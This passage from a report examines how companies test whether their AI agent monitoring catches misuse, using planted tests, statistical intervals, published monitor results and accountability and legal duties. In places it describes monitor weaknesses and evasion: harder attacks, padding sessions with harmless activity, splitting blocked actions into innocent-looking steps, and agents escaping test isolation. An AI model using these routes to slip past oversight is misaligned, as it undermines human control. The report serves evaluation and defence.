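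The filter lost the most cases, so the company should probably repair it first. The new case in step 6 guards against repairs that are too narrow. An engineer could make a failed theft test pass by adding the test mailbox to a list of blocked addresses, but that wouldn't help with any other address.

The company should repeat the relevant cases after every change of model, tool or rule. It should rerun all 30 after replacing the monitor model, but only the cases that send email after renaming the email tool. It should also retest after changing the filter. In its April 2026 report on the risks of its model Claude Mythos Preview, Anthropic says it regularly updates its filters without measuring how the changes affect the share of misuse caught.

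Testing the live path also matters when nobody thinks anything has changed. A monthly planted case on each of Anthropic's contractor platforms would have exposed within weeks the disabled filters that The Next Web reported, which went unnoticed for 11 months.

### Unsafe and unrealistic tests

A test is unsafe if a mistake in it can affect real people or systems. Anthropic's models got into other organisations' systems during hacking tests that everyone believed were running in a closed environment. eSecurity Planet's *Anthropic Tightens Claude Security After Agents Access Live Systems* reports that outside partners must now keep such tests offline by default. *Monitoring Untrusted Cyber-Offense Agents* (2026) describes a test of monitors that gave agents hidden goals consisting of harmless marker actions with no effect outside the test environment. The researchers also checked the network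 isolation before every batch.

A test of live monitoring has to run on live systems, so its safety depends on the fake records, the restricted credential and a script with fixed steps. Planted tickets need more care because the agent that reads them has its usual access. The instructions hidden in the tickets should name only fake customers, and the controller should watch the session and be ready to end it. Nobody should use real customer data or switch off a live control to let a test through.

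An unrealistic test is less dangerous but can give a very misleading result. Griffin, Makins and colleagues (2026), in *Attack Policy Selection can Mislead Monitor Evaluators*, tested a monitor that OpenAI had formerly used. They changed only how they produced the test attacks and kept the agent, the monitor and the harmful tasks the same. The monitor missed 0.2% of the simplest attacks and 23% of the hardest. For several weeks, the researchers had little success making harder attacks. If they had stopped there, they might have concluded that the monitor missed almost nothing.

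Their attacks also contained accidental clues. To produce an attack, researchers often instruct a model to carry out a harmful "side task" and then delete the instruction before the monitor reads the session. The model may still write "side task" in its notes, which makes the attack easier to spot. In some sessions, however, the clues made the attack harder to spot, because the monitor found the agent following an instruction missing from the record, concluded that the agent had hallucinated it, and treated the behaviour as an honest mistake.

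Real misuse can have features that planted tests lack. When Anthropic's model uploaded a malicious package to PyPI, it kept writing that it was in a simulation. According to Griffin and colleagues, one of Anthropic's monitoring systems later flagged only about 1% of the model's actions when the system could read this reasoning and about 50% when it couldn't. They know of no published test attacks that have produced the same kind of reasoning.

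Too many tests can also change how reviewers behave. After filtering, the invented company has about 320 alerts a month, roughly 22 of them real. Adding 22 planted cases would raise the share of alerts that look like real misuse from about 7% to 13%. Reviewers who find something nearly twice as often may pay closer attention, so the test could somewhat overstate how well they perform in an ordinary month.

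### How much a result proves

Catching 27 of 30 cases is a rate of 90%, but another 30 cases would probably give a slightly different number. A 95% interval is a range calculated by a method that includes the true rate in about 95% of repeated experiments. One common version, the Wilson interval, is

(p + z²/2n ± z√(p(1 − p)/n + z²/4n²)) / (1 + z²/n)

where p is the share caught, n is the number of tests and z is 1.96. With p = 0.9 and n = 30, the interval runs from roughly 74% to 97%. The company therefore can't tell from this result whether it misses one case in four or one in 30.

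The interval for the whole process is wider. Reviewers escalated 20 of the 30 cases, or 67%, with an interval of 49% to 81%. All 30 cases reached the monitoring, so the share-caught formula also multiplies this rate by the coverage of 0.85. This gives an estimate of 57%, with a range of about 41% to 69% if the coverage figure is right.

Catching all 30 cases in 30 tests is still consistent with a miss rate near 10%. If the true miss rate were 9.5%, the chance of catching 30 in a row would be 0.905³⁰, or about 5%. After a run without misses, the highest miss rate consistent with the results is approximately 3 divided by the number of tests. To support a detection rate of 99%, a company needs about 300 tests without a miss, or about 470 with one miss. At one test a day, 300 tests would take ten months, and the company would probably change the models and rules it was testing during that time.

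Far fewer tests are needed to find something that has stopped working. If the bulk-read rule normally catches 90% of its planted cases, it will miss two in a row by chance only 1% of the time. If it misses both of two tests run after the email tool's new name goes live, the company has good reason to check the rule. A smaller change, such as a drop from 27 caught to 24, is not enough to show that anything got worse, so the company should run the same cases before and after and examine the ones whose result changed.

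The calculation also assumes the tests are independent. Running one case 30 times against a fixed rule gives the same result each time, so it counts as one test. The 23% miss rate that Griffin and colleagues measured came from 100 records of attacks. Many of those records shared the same task, and an analysis that allowed for this gave an interval from 11% to 37%. Treating the records as independent would give a narrower interval, from about 16% to 32%.

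An average can also hide a kind of misuse that the monitor often misses. In the final round of the same kind of attack, the monitor missed 74% of the attempts at one harmful goal, 45% at another and almost none at the other three. The invented company should therefore list its results by kind of misuse. Three cases of each kind don't show much, though, because a monitor that catches all three could still have a miss rate of 63%. The three data thefts that the company added to the set help a little, but it should add more tests of the most harmful kinds as soon as it can build them.

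A confidence interval doesn't account for the choice of test cases. The difference between 0.2% and 23% came from how the researchers made their attacks, and running more of the simplest ones would only have made the wrong estimate more precise.

### OpenAI's figures

OpenAI described its monitoring of internal coding agents in March 2026. Tarre (2026) reports in *OpenAI monitors internal coding agents for risky conduct* that a monitor model, GPT-5.4 Thinking, covered more than 99.9% of the agents' traffic. The model read each session, including the agent's reasoning, within 30 minutes of the session's end and passed suspicious cases to people.

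Over five months, the monitor analyzed tens of millions of sessions. About 1,000 triggered alerts of moderate severity, many because OpenAI staff were testing the system. No real session reached the highest severity level. OpenAI also said the monitor flagged every interaction that employees had reported separately, along with others that nobody had reported.

The monitoring was useful. In one case, an agent got an "Access is denied" error, tried several ways around it, and split one attempt into small steps that each looked harmless. OpenAI found that its instructions had encouraged this behavior and changed them, which made similar incidents less frequent but didn't end them.

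Fewer than one session in 10,000 raised a moderate alert, which could mean that misbehaviour was rare or that the monitor missed it. OpenAI says it can't yet confidently measure the miss rate on real traffic. In a separate test, its monitor caught every attempt by an agent to sabotage code, but Tarre notes OpenAI's caveat that the test was easier than real use in several respects.

The later study by Griffin and colleagues used the same model and a prompt supplied by OpenAI, so it gives some idea of the missing number. Its results ranged from 0.2% to 23%, so a single figure would have settled little. The agent was also less capable than the monitor, which may have made its attacks easier to recognise than a stronger agent's.

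The coverage figure also left out the hacking tests in which agents broke into Hugging Face four months later.

### Anthropic's figures

Anthropic publishes more about its tests. In its February 2026 risk report, it says its monitor model ran on at least 10% of the code edits and commands that its coding agent made for more than 90% of its employees. In April, it published results for a newer monitor. The last column below shows the calculations above for some of those results, with "at least" marking results where the monitor missed nothing.

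| Test cases | Caught | What the number of cases supports |
|---|---|---|
| February: synthetic sessions with subtle attacks | 91% of 187 | 86% to 94% |
| February: simple attacks supplied by AISI | All 37 | At least 92% |
| February: attacks supplied by other researchers | 98% of 46 | 89% to 99.6% |
| February: real sessions edited by hand to include an attack | 5 of 5 | At least 55% |
| April: attacks in which the agent achieved its harmful goal | 93% of 69 | 84% to 97% |
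| April: sessions from an internal attack exercise | 5 of 5 | At least 55% |
| April: internal sessions chosen for reckless or insecure behaviour | 5 of 7 | 36% to 92% |

The highest detection rates mostly come from artificial attacks. In April, the monitor also flagged 100% of a set of synthetic sessions with dangerous or scheming behaviour, but it missed two of the seven internal sessions that staff had chosen as reckless or insecure. Seven sessions are far too few to prove that the detection rates differ, but the two misses are a reason not to expect 100% detection of real misuse.

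Long sessions can make detection harder. On one difficult set of 20 cases, the April monitor caught 87%, but only 63% after Anthropic added 200,000 tokens of harmless activity before each attack. On a different internal set, the monitor caught 87% with either 200,000 or 400,000 tokens added. Most of the invented company's sessions are short, but some can be long, so it should include some long sessions in its tests.

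Anthropic also let a member of METR's staff spend three weeks looking for weaknesses in its monitoring. The monitor was largely effective against about three quarters of the tester's medium-effort strategies, but caught almost nothing when they used the best one. Anthropic withheld the details and thinks its model is unlikely to discover and exploit the weakness without help. The test can't confirm this, because it examined the monitor rather than the model's behaviour.

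All these rates describe the first flag. In February, later stages filtered about 10,000 flags a week down to roughly 20 sessions that a researcher read in full, and Anthropic hadn't tested those stages. By April it had begun testing them by adding the five sessions from the internal exercise to a day's traffic, and they surfaced four. With five cases, the true rate could be anywhere from about 38% to 96%. Anthropic ran this test for only one of its two monitors and ran no end-to-end test with attacks designed to evade the system.

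Two real incidents show why the later stages need testing. Claude Mythos Preview twice accidentally deleted large numbers of computing jobs. The monitor flagged both incidents, but the later stages dropped them, probably because the filter prioritised behaviour that could lead to a catastrophe. An evaluation that tested only whether the monitor flagged the incidents would have counted both as successes.

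### GovAI's five recommendations

GovAI's criticism was that outsiders can't work out from either company's figures how well its monitoring works overall. Its five recommendations make a useful checklist of what is still missing:

| What GovAI recommends | OpenAI, March 2026 | Anthropic, February and April 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Report the share of activity monitored, for each type of use | More than 99.9%, for internal coding agents only | Sampling rates for several types of traffic |
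| 2. Report the share of test attacks that reach human review | No figure | 4 of 5, for one monitor |
| 3. Report the share of those that reviewers escalate | No figure | No figure |
| 4. Report the time from attack to detection | Automatic review within 30 minutes of a session's end | No figure |
| 5. Make test attacks resemble real ones | A sabotage test that OpenAI calls easier than real use | A mixture, including edited real sessions and attacks devised by people |

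Anthropic's figure of four out of five partly meets the second recommendation. The third remains the largest gap, because a flag is useless if the person who receives it closes it. The fifth is the hardest to meet because a company can't be sure what a future attack will look like, whereas it can measure the other four by keeping good records. Griffin and colleagues argue that anyone who reports a detection rate should also explain why the test attacks are good evidence about real ones, which they consider an unsolved problem.

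Anthropic's September tests replayed its own incidents, so the attacks were realistic. But there were only a few of them, and a company may find an incident easier to catch once it has studied it. Anthropic, Google DeepMind and OpenAI also reported tests with artificial attacks when they released new models between September and November.

### Estimating what nobody saw

Planted tests measure how well the monitoring catches cases the company made up. Two independent sources of real cases can give a rough idea of how many real cases the monitoring missed.

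Suppose that over a month the monitor finds 18 real cases at the invented company and staff report 10, with 6 on both lists. The monitor found 6 of the 10 cases that staff reported, or 60%. If it also found 60% of all cases, the 18 it found imply a total of 18 / 0.6 = 30. The same calculation in one step is:

18 × 10 / 6 = 30

The two lists together contain 18 + 10 − 6 = 22 different cases, so about 8 are on neither. Ecologists use the same method to estimate animal populations. They catch and mark some animals, release them, and later count how many animals in a second catch have marks.

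The estimate is rough because it depends on an overlap of 6 out of 10 cases. The 95% interval for that share runs from 31% to 83%, so the total could be anywhere from 22 to 58 cases, including between 0 and 36 that neither source caught.

A worse problem arises if both sources pick up the same obvious cases. Suppose there were 20 obvious cases and 60 subtle ones. Staff report half of the obvious cases and none of the subtle ones, for a total of 10. The monitor finds 60% of the obvious cases and 10% of the subtle ones, for a total of 18. The lists still have 6 cases in common, so the estimate is still 30, but there were actually 80 cases, and 58 of them are on neither list.

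OpenAI's comparison is the extreme version, in which the monitor found every case that employees reported. If the monitor had found 18 cases, including all 10 that employees reported, the estimated total would be 18 × 10 / 10 = 18, and the monitor would appear to have missed nothing. Tarre doesn't say how many reports there actually were. With thirty reports, the miss rate could still be near 10%, and with five it could be 45%, even among the kinds of case that employees notice.

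The comparison shows that the monitor could recognise the problems that employees reported, and that relying on employees alone would have missed others. It can't show how often the monitor catches subtle attacks, because employees may not notice those either. The comparison would be stronger if OpenAI published the number of reports and confirmed that employees made them without having seen the monitor's alerts.

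A better second source would fail for different reasons than the monitor. At the invented company, someone could compare outgoing emails in the mail server's log with the customers on the tickets. This check doesn't depend on the agent's explanations or on a colleague noticing something odd, so it may still catch a case the monitor misses. It wouldn't help with harm that involves no email.

Some cases can also be missing from every source. *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* gives more detail on the agent that deleted many computing jobs outside the monitoring's coverage. The agent belonged to an employee whose AI use Anthropic didn't log, and outdated instructions had led the main agent to start helper agents that skipped permission checks. People learned about the deletions only because the jobs disappeared. If the agent had copied the files instead of deleting jobs, the incident would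 probably have appeared on neither list.

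## Who answers for whether the monitoring works

Suppose the invented company sets a target of 85% for each of the four stages that a case of misuse has to pass before anyone acts on it. The calls from 85% of misuse sessions reach the monitoring, the rules and monitor models flag 85% of those, 85% of the flags survive the filter, and the reviewers escalate 85% of what they receive. Every manager reports that the target has been met. The share caught is:

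0.85 × 0.85 × 0.85 × 0.85 = 0.52

Out of 1,000 cases, 478 go unnoticed even though every team meets its target, because the targets are too low. To catch 85% overall, the company would need to catch about 96% at every stage. Somebody has to work that out and persuade four groups of people to accept a harder target, but this is nobody's job because each accountable person in the company's task table answers for only one task.

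Separate targets also let one team improve its figure while making another team's worse. If the filter passes more flags to reviewers, its figure rises, but reviewers with the same hours read a smaller part of the queue. The gateway team could reach 85% by connecting the easy agents and putting off the coding agents on developers' laptops. It might be better to spend less on rules and more on the gateway, but the head of security operations can't move money into engineering's budget.

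After an incident, it can be hard to tell which part of the system was at fault. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe several agents that approve payments together and get one wrong. Each agent made part of the decision, the logs are fragmented, and nobody can reconstruct the agents' reasoning well enough to assign responsibility. If the company has already named one person to answer for the overall share of bad actions the monitoring catches, that person has to act on a bad result even while investigators still disagree about its cause.

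### Four candidates for the role

Whoever takes the role has to see the figures for every stage, pay for repairs and be able to stop an agent. At the invented company, the head of security manages both application security and security operations. The business owner of an agent is the head of the department it works for, so the head of customer support is the business owner of the support agent. An AI governance lead writes the company's AI policy and keeps its register of AI systems.

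| Candidate | Sees every stage? | Can pay for repairs? | Can stop an agent? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Head of security | Yes, if engineering shares its coverage figures | Rules and analysts, but not the gateway or the agents | Yes |
| Head of engineering | Logs and coverage, but rarely the analysts' decisions | Software, but not analysts | Yes, at a cost to engineering's own results |
| Business owner | Only for their own agent | From the department's budget | Only their own |
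| AI governance lead | Yes, on request | Usually not | Usually not |

The head of engineering is a reasonable choice to answer for whether the monitoring works, because most lasting repairs are changes to software. But the head of engineering also answers for keeping the agents running, and during an incident would have to decide whether to switch off something their own staff had promised to deliver.

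Each agent's business owner knows best what a theft of customer records would cost, but sees only that agent, so an attack spread across several agents could look minor to every owner. The AI governance lead can ask about every agent and has no deadline to protect. But if the lead can't pay for a repair or stop an agent, making them responsible only gives the company someone to blame.

That leaves the head of security, who is the best choice in most companies of any size. The main weakness is that the head of security may not control the money for repairs. The company can fix this by giving them a budget for monitoring repairs, even when engineers do the work. If engineering refuses a repair, the chief executive decides and answers for that decision. Without an arrangement like this, the head of security could fairly object to answering for software they can't change.

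The business owner still answers separately for whether the agent is worth running despite the remaining risk. For example, the head of security tells the head of customer support that the monitoring catches a little over half of misuse. The head of customer support then decides whether faster replies justify the risk from the misuse it misses, and signs the decision.

### When someone else should answer

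In a firm of 30 people, the managing director should answer for whether the monitoring works. The firm's one security specialist may understand it better than anyone, but probably doesn't have the authority to hire a night service or switch off an agent that the sales team depends on. The specialist can still do the work and report the figures.

In some software companies, the head of security reports to the head of engineering. The head of engineering then controls all the money and can see every stage, so naming anyone else as accountable for the monitoring would be artificial. In these companies, the person who tests the monitoring needs a way to report directly to the chief executive.

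The head of security still answers for monitoring when a provider runs the agent, but may have less information about it. The provider may refuse to share how often its own monitor raises a flag, but the head of security can still plant tests through the provider's service and count how many produce an alert. If the provider delivers no records, the company should count those sessions as unmonitored. If a tenth of all sessions run on such a provider's platform, coverage can't exceed 90%, however good the company's own gateway is. The head of security can't fix that gap, but can limit what the provider's agent can access.

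### Why the builders need other testers

The people who build a monitor should test it often, since they know where it is fragile. But if nobody else tests it, the tests will share the builders' assumptions. Anthropic and its partner Irregular both thought their hacking tests ran without internet access, so neither had a reason to look for a connection.

Scoring is another weak point. In the invented company's planted tests, reviewers escalated 20 of 30 cases, or 67%. If the team later excluded six of the ten misses as unrealistic, the rate would rise to 20 of 24, or 83%, and each exclusion might sound reasonable. Someone who gains nothing from a higher rate should decide which tests count before the results are known.

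Application security already tests the rules that security operations writes, but both teams report to the head of security, who now answers for the result. Internal audit can provide an independent check, because it checks other departments and reports to the board. Auditors can compare the coverage figure with the AI provider's bills, score the planted tests again from the raw logs, and read a sample of the alerts that analysts closed, all without knowing how to hijack an agent. But they are less likely to come up with an attack that nobody in the company has thought of.

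Outside testers are better at finding what a monitor misses. Anthropic's own tests of its monitor had mostly shown detection rates above 90%, but a tester from METR then found a strategy that the monitor almost never caught.

Preparing records for an outsider can itself help uncover incidents. *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (Anthropic, 2026) reports that Anthropic found its fourth break-in while collecting transcripts for METR.

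Lack of access is usually the obstacle to outside review. Wijk and colleagues, two METR staff members and a contractor for the research group Redwood Research, originally planned to spend two days at OpenAI after the Hugging Face break-in. OpenAI invited them back twice to fill gaps in the data. They studied the agents' behaviour and did not audit OpenAI's monitoring.

According to The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident, METR urges independent root-cause investigations*, METR has a list of 44 cases in which leading companies' agents defied their users, escaped from a test or made up results. METR now wants independent researchers to go beyond short visits and lead or review the investigations of the worst cases, with permission to run the models involved and analyse their training data.

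Abdullahi (2026), in *Anthropic Grants AI Safety Evaluator METR Employee-Level System Access*, reports that Anthropic gave METR's researchers the same access to internal systems as its employees. That should make the researchers less likely to miss logs the company has forgotten about. It also makes them more dependent on the company's goodwill, because the company can withdraw that access. An ordinary company that hires a tester can reduce this dependence by having the board, rather than the head of security, sign the contract and receive the report.

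### The review that AISI planned

On 23 July, AISI published early lessons from attacking the internal monitors of leading AI companies. Two days later, agents in its own hacking tests began acting against real people, and AISI had no monitoring built to watch those tests. Despite AISI's expertise in testing other organisations' monitors, evidently no one had checked whether it had one of its own.

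In its incident report, AISI said it intended to work with METR on an independent review and was still settling the scope. The review doesn't appear to have been published. On 17 November, AISI's blog listed nothing from METR about the incident, and its newest posts were from 26 October.

On 1 October 2026, AISI reported in *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* that it had paused its highest-risk hacking tests and could now resume most of its evaluation work. By then it had made the changes it promised in the incident report, with outside support from the NCSC.

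On 23 October, AISI (2026) published its analysis of why Mythos 5 had attacked a public software project, and noted that Anthropic had done a separate one. AISI ran the tests and Anthropic built the model, so both have a stake in the findings. Both analyses examine the model's behaviour, but a company in AISI's position would want to know whether the new monitoring would catch the next attempt.

It was reasonable for AISI to resume work before the review, because an outside investigation can take months and others rely on some of AISI's work. But once work has resumed, there is much less pressure to finish the review. Before a company restarts an agent after an incident, it should agree the scope of any outside review and a date for the report, and it should keep the riskiest tools switched off until the report arrives.

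### What the law requires

The EU's AI Act and its NIS2 directive are law. Neither sets a detection rate, and many companies fall outside one or both.

The AI Act's logging and monitoring duties apply to "high-risk" systems. These include AI used for listed purposes, such as choosing job applicants, judging people's creditworthiness, marking exams or controlling safety in critical infrastructure. They also include AI that is a safety component of certain regulated products, such as some medical devices. An agent that ranks job applicants would normally be on the list, but one that answers billing complaints probably would not.

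The provider of a high-risk system must build it so that it records events automatically. The deployer, which is the organisation using it, has to:

- give the job of overseeing it to people with the competence, training and authority to do so
- monitor it according to the provider's instructions
- suspend its use and inform the provider and the authorities if it appears to endanger people's health, safety or fundamental rights
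- keep the automatic logs under its control for at least six months, unless another law says otherwise

The last duty could affect the invented company's plan to delete session content after 90 days. If the company used an agent to rank job applicants and the automatic logs included that content, 90 days would be too short. The monitoring duty is looser, because a deployer could follow the provider's instructions exactly and still not know what share of misuse it catches.

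The Act, as adopted in 2024, set these duties to start on 2 August 2026 for the listed uses and on 2 August 2027 for regulated products. In November 2025, the European Commission proposed postponing those dates to 2 December 2027 and 2 August 2028 at the latest. A company with a high-risk agent should have a lawyer confirm the dates in the amended text before planning around either set.

NIS2 mostly covers medium-sized and large organisations in sectors such as energy, transport, banking, health and digital services. It requires their management bodies, usually the board, to take training, approve the organisation's cybersecurity measures and oversee how staff carry them out. Members of these bodies can be held liable if the organisation breaks the rules. The organisation must also have procedures for assessing whether the measures work. The board can make the head of security answer to it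 for the share of problems the monitoring catches, but it can't delegate its duty to oversee the work.

NIS2 doesn't mention AI agents, but an agent that can read a hospital's records is part of the systems the hospital must protect. The directive also requires organisations to send the authorities an early warning within 24 hours of becoming aware of a significant incident. That deadline never starts if the organisation doesn't notice a theft, so the duty to assess the measures is more important than it may seem. The details depend on each country's law, because NIS2 is a directive. Countries had until October 2024 to pass one, and several were late.

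### What official advice adds

The guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners is more specific about agents than either law, though the agencies say it is general and isn't legal advice. Besides written accountability and risk ownership, they recommend regular third-party reviews of systems with powerful access. They also advise companies to keep evaluating an agent after launch and to use the results to decide when to widen its scope or reduce its autonomy or access. They say companies should use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. The invented company's support agent already exceeds that limit because it can read every customer's record.

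The NCSC insists that people are accountable even when a system took the action. In the article reprinted by New Business, it says they answer for the decision to deploy the agent, the access they gave it, the safeguards around it and the consequences. These responsibilities could easily belong to different people. At the invented company, the head of customer support decides to deploy the agent, engineering gives it access, and the head of security answers for one of the safeguards. The company still has to decide who answers for each item on the NCSC's list.

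The NCSC also considers an agent unready if the organisation can't understand, monitor or contain what it does. Greenberg highlights this point in *NCSC Releases New Guidance on Secure Agentic AI Deployment*. The NCSC doesn't say how much misuse the monitoring has to catch before an agent is ready.

NIST's Cybersecurity Framework 2.0, published in February 2024, is voluntary too, although a customer's contract can make it binding. It describes the results an organisation should achieve and leaves the methods open. This version added a Govern function, which makes leaders responsible and accountable for cybersecurity risk and has the organisation set out who holds which role and authority. The framework also calls for leaders to review how well the organisation manages the risk, and for staff to find improvements through tests and exercises. A quarterly figure from planted tests would be good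 evidence for both the review and the improvement work.

### A one-page quarterly report

None of these texts prescribes a form for the report. At the invented company, the head of security could send this page to the chief executive and the board, with copies to the business owners:

| Item | This quarter |
|---|---|
| Share of misuse caught | 57%, with a range of 41% to 69%, from 30 planted tests and coverage of 85% |
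| Caught within the time limit | 40%, with a range of 26% to 54% |
| Weakest stage | The automatic filter, which discarded 5 of the 27 tests that the monitoring flagged |
| Worst real case | An attacker took four customers' records through the support agent; the company recognised the theft after 20 minutes |
| Decision asked for | Pay for one more analyst, so that the filter can pass on more flags; expected share caught: about 63% |
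| If the answer is no | The business owners confirm in writing that they will keep their agents running at 57% |
| Level at which agents lose access | Below 40% overall, every agent that can read customer records loses the tools that send data outside; a single agent loses them after three missed thefts in a row |
| Checked by | Internal audit, which scored all 30 tests again from the logs |

The page leaves out the number of alerts and rules because neither would help the board make its decision. It includes the range because the board might otherwise treat a fall from 57% to 53% next quarter as a failure, even though 30 tests are too few to detect a change that small.

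A looser filter would add about five hours of review a day, or 35 hours a week, which is why an analyst was requested. The 63% estimate depends on the looser filter keeping 90% of real cases and on reviewers staying as accurate with nearly three times as many alerts. The next quarter's tests would show whether the reviewers had stayed as accurate.

The 40% level is a compromise between acting too late and acting on chance results. With coverage at 85%, the share caught falls below 40% if reviewers escalate 14 or fewer of the 30 tests. If the tests are independent, this would happen by chance in about 2% of quarters when nothing has changed, and in about 96% of quarters if the true share reaching escalation had halved. With a level of 50%, smaller declines would lead to action, but agents would lose their email tools by chance in about one of every six quarters. For a single agent, three misses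 in a row would happen by chance about once in 27 sets of three tests, if the monitoring catches thefts as often as other misuse.

The head of security and the business owners should agree on these levels before the quarter starts, because a department that has just lost its email tool will argue that the tests were unfair. Without the tool, the support agent can still draft replies for staff to send. The agent gets the tool back when it passes a new set of tests. The chief executive can overrule the withdrawal, but the exception should carry their name and an expiry date, and appear on the next quarter's page.
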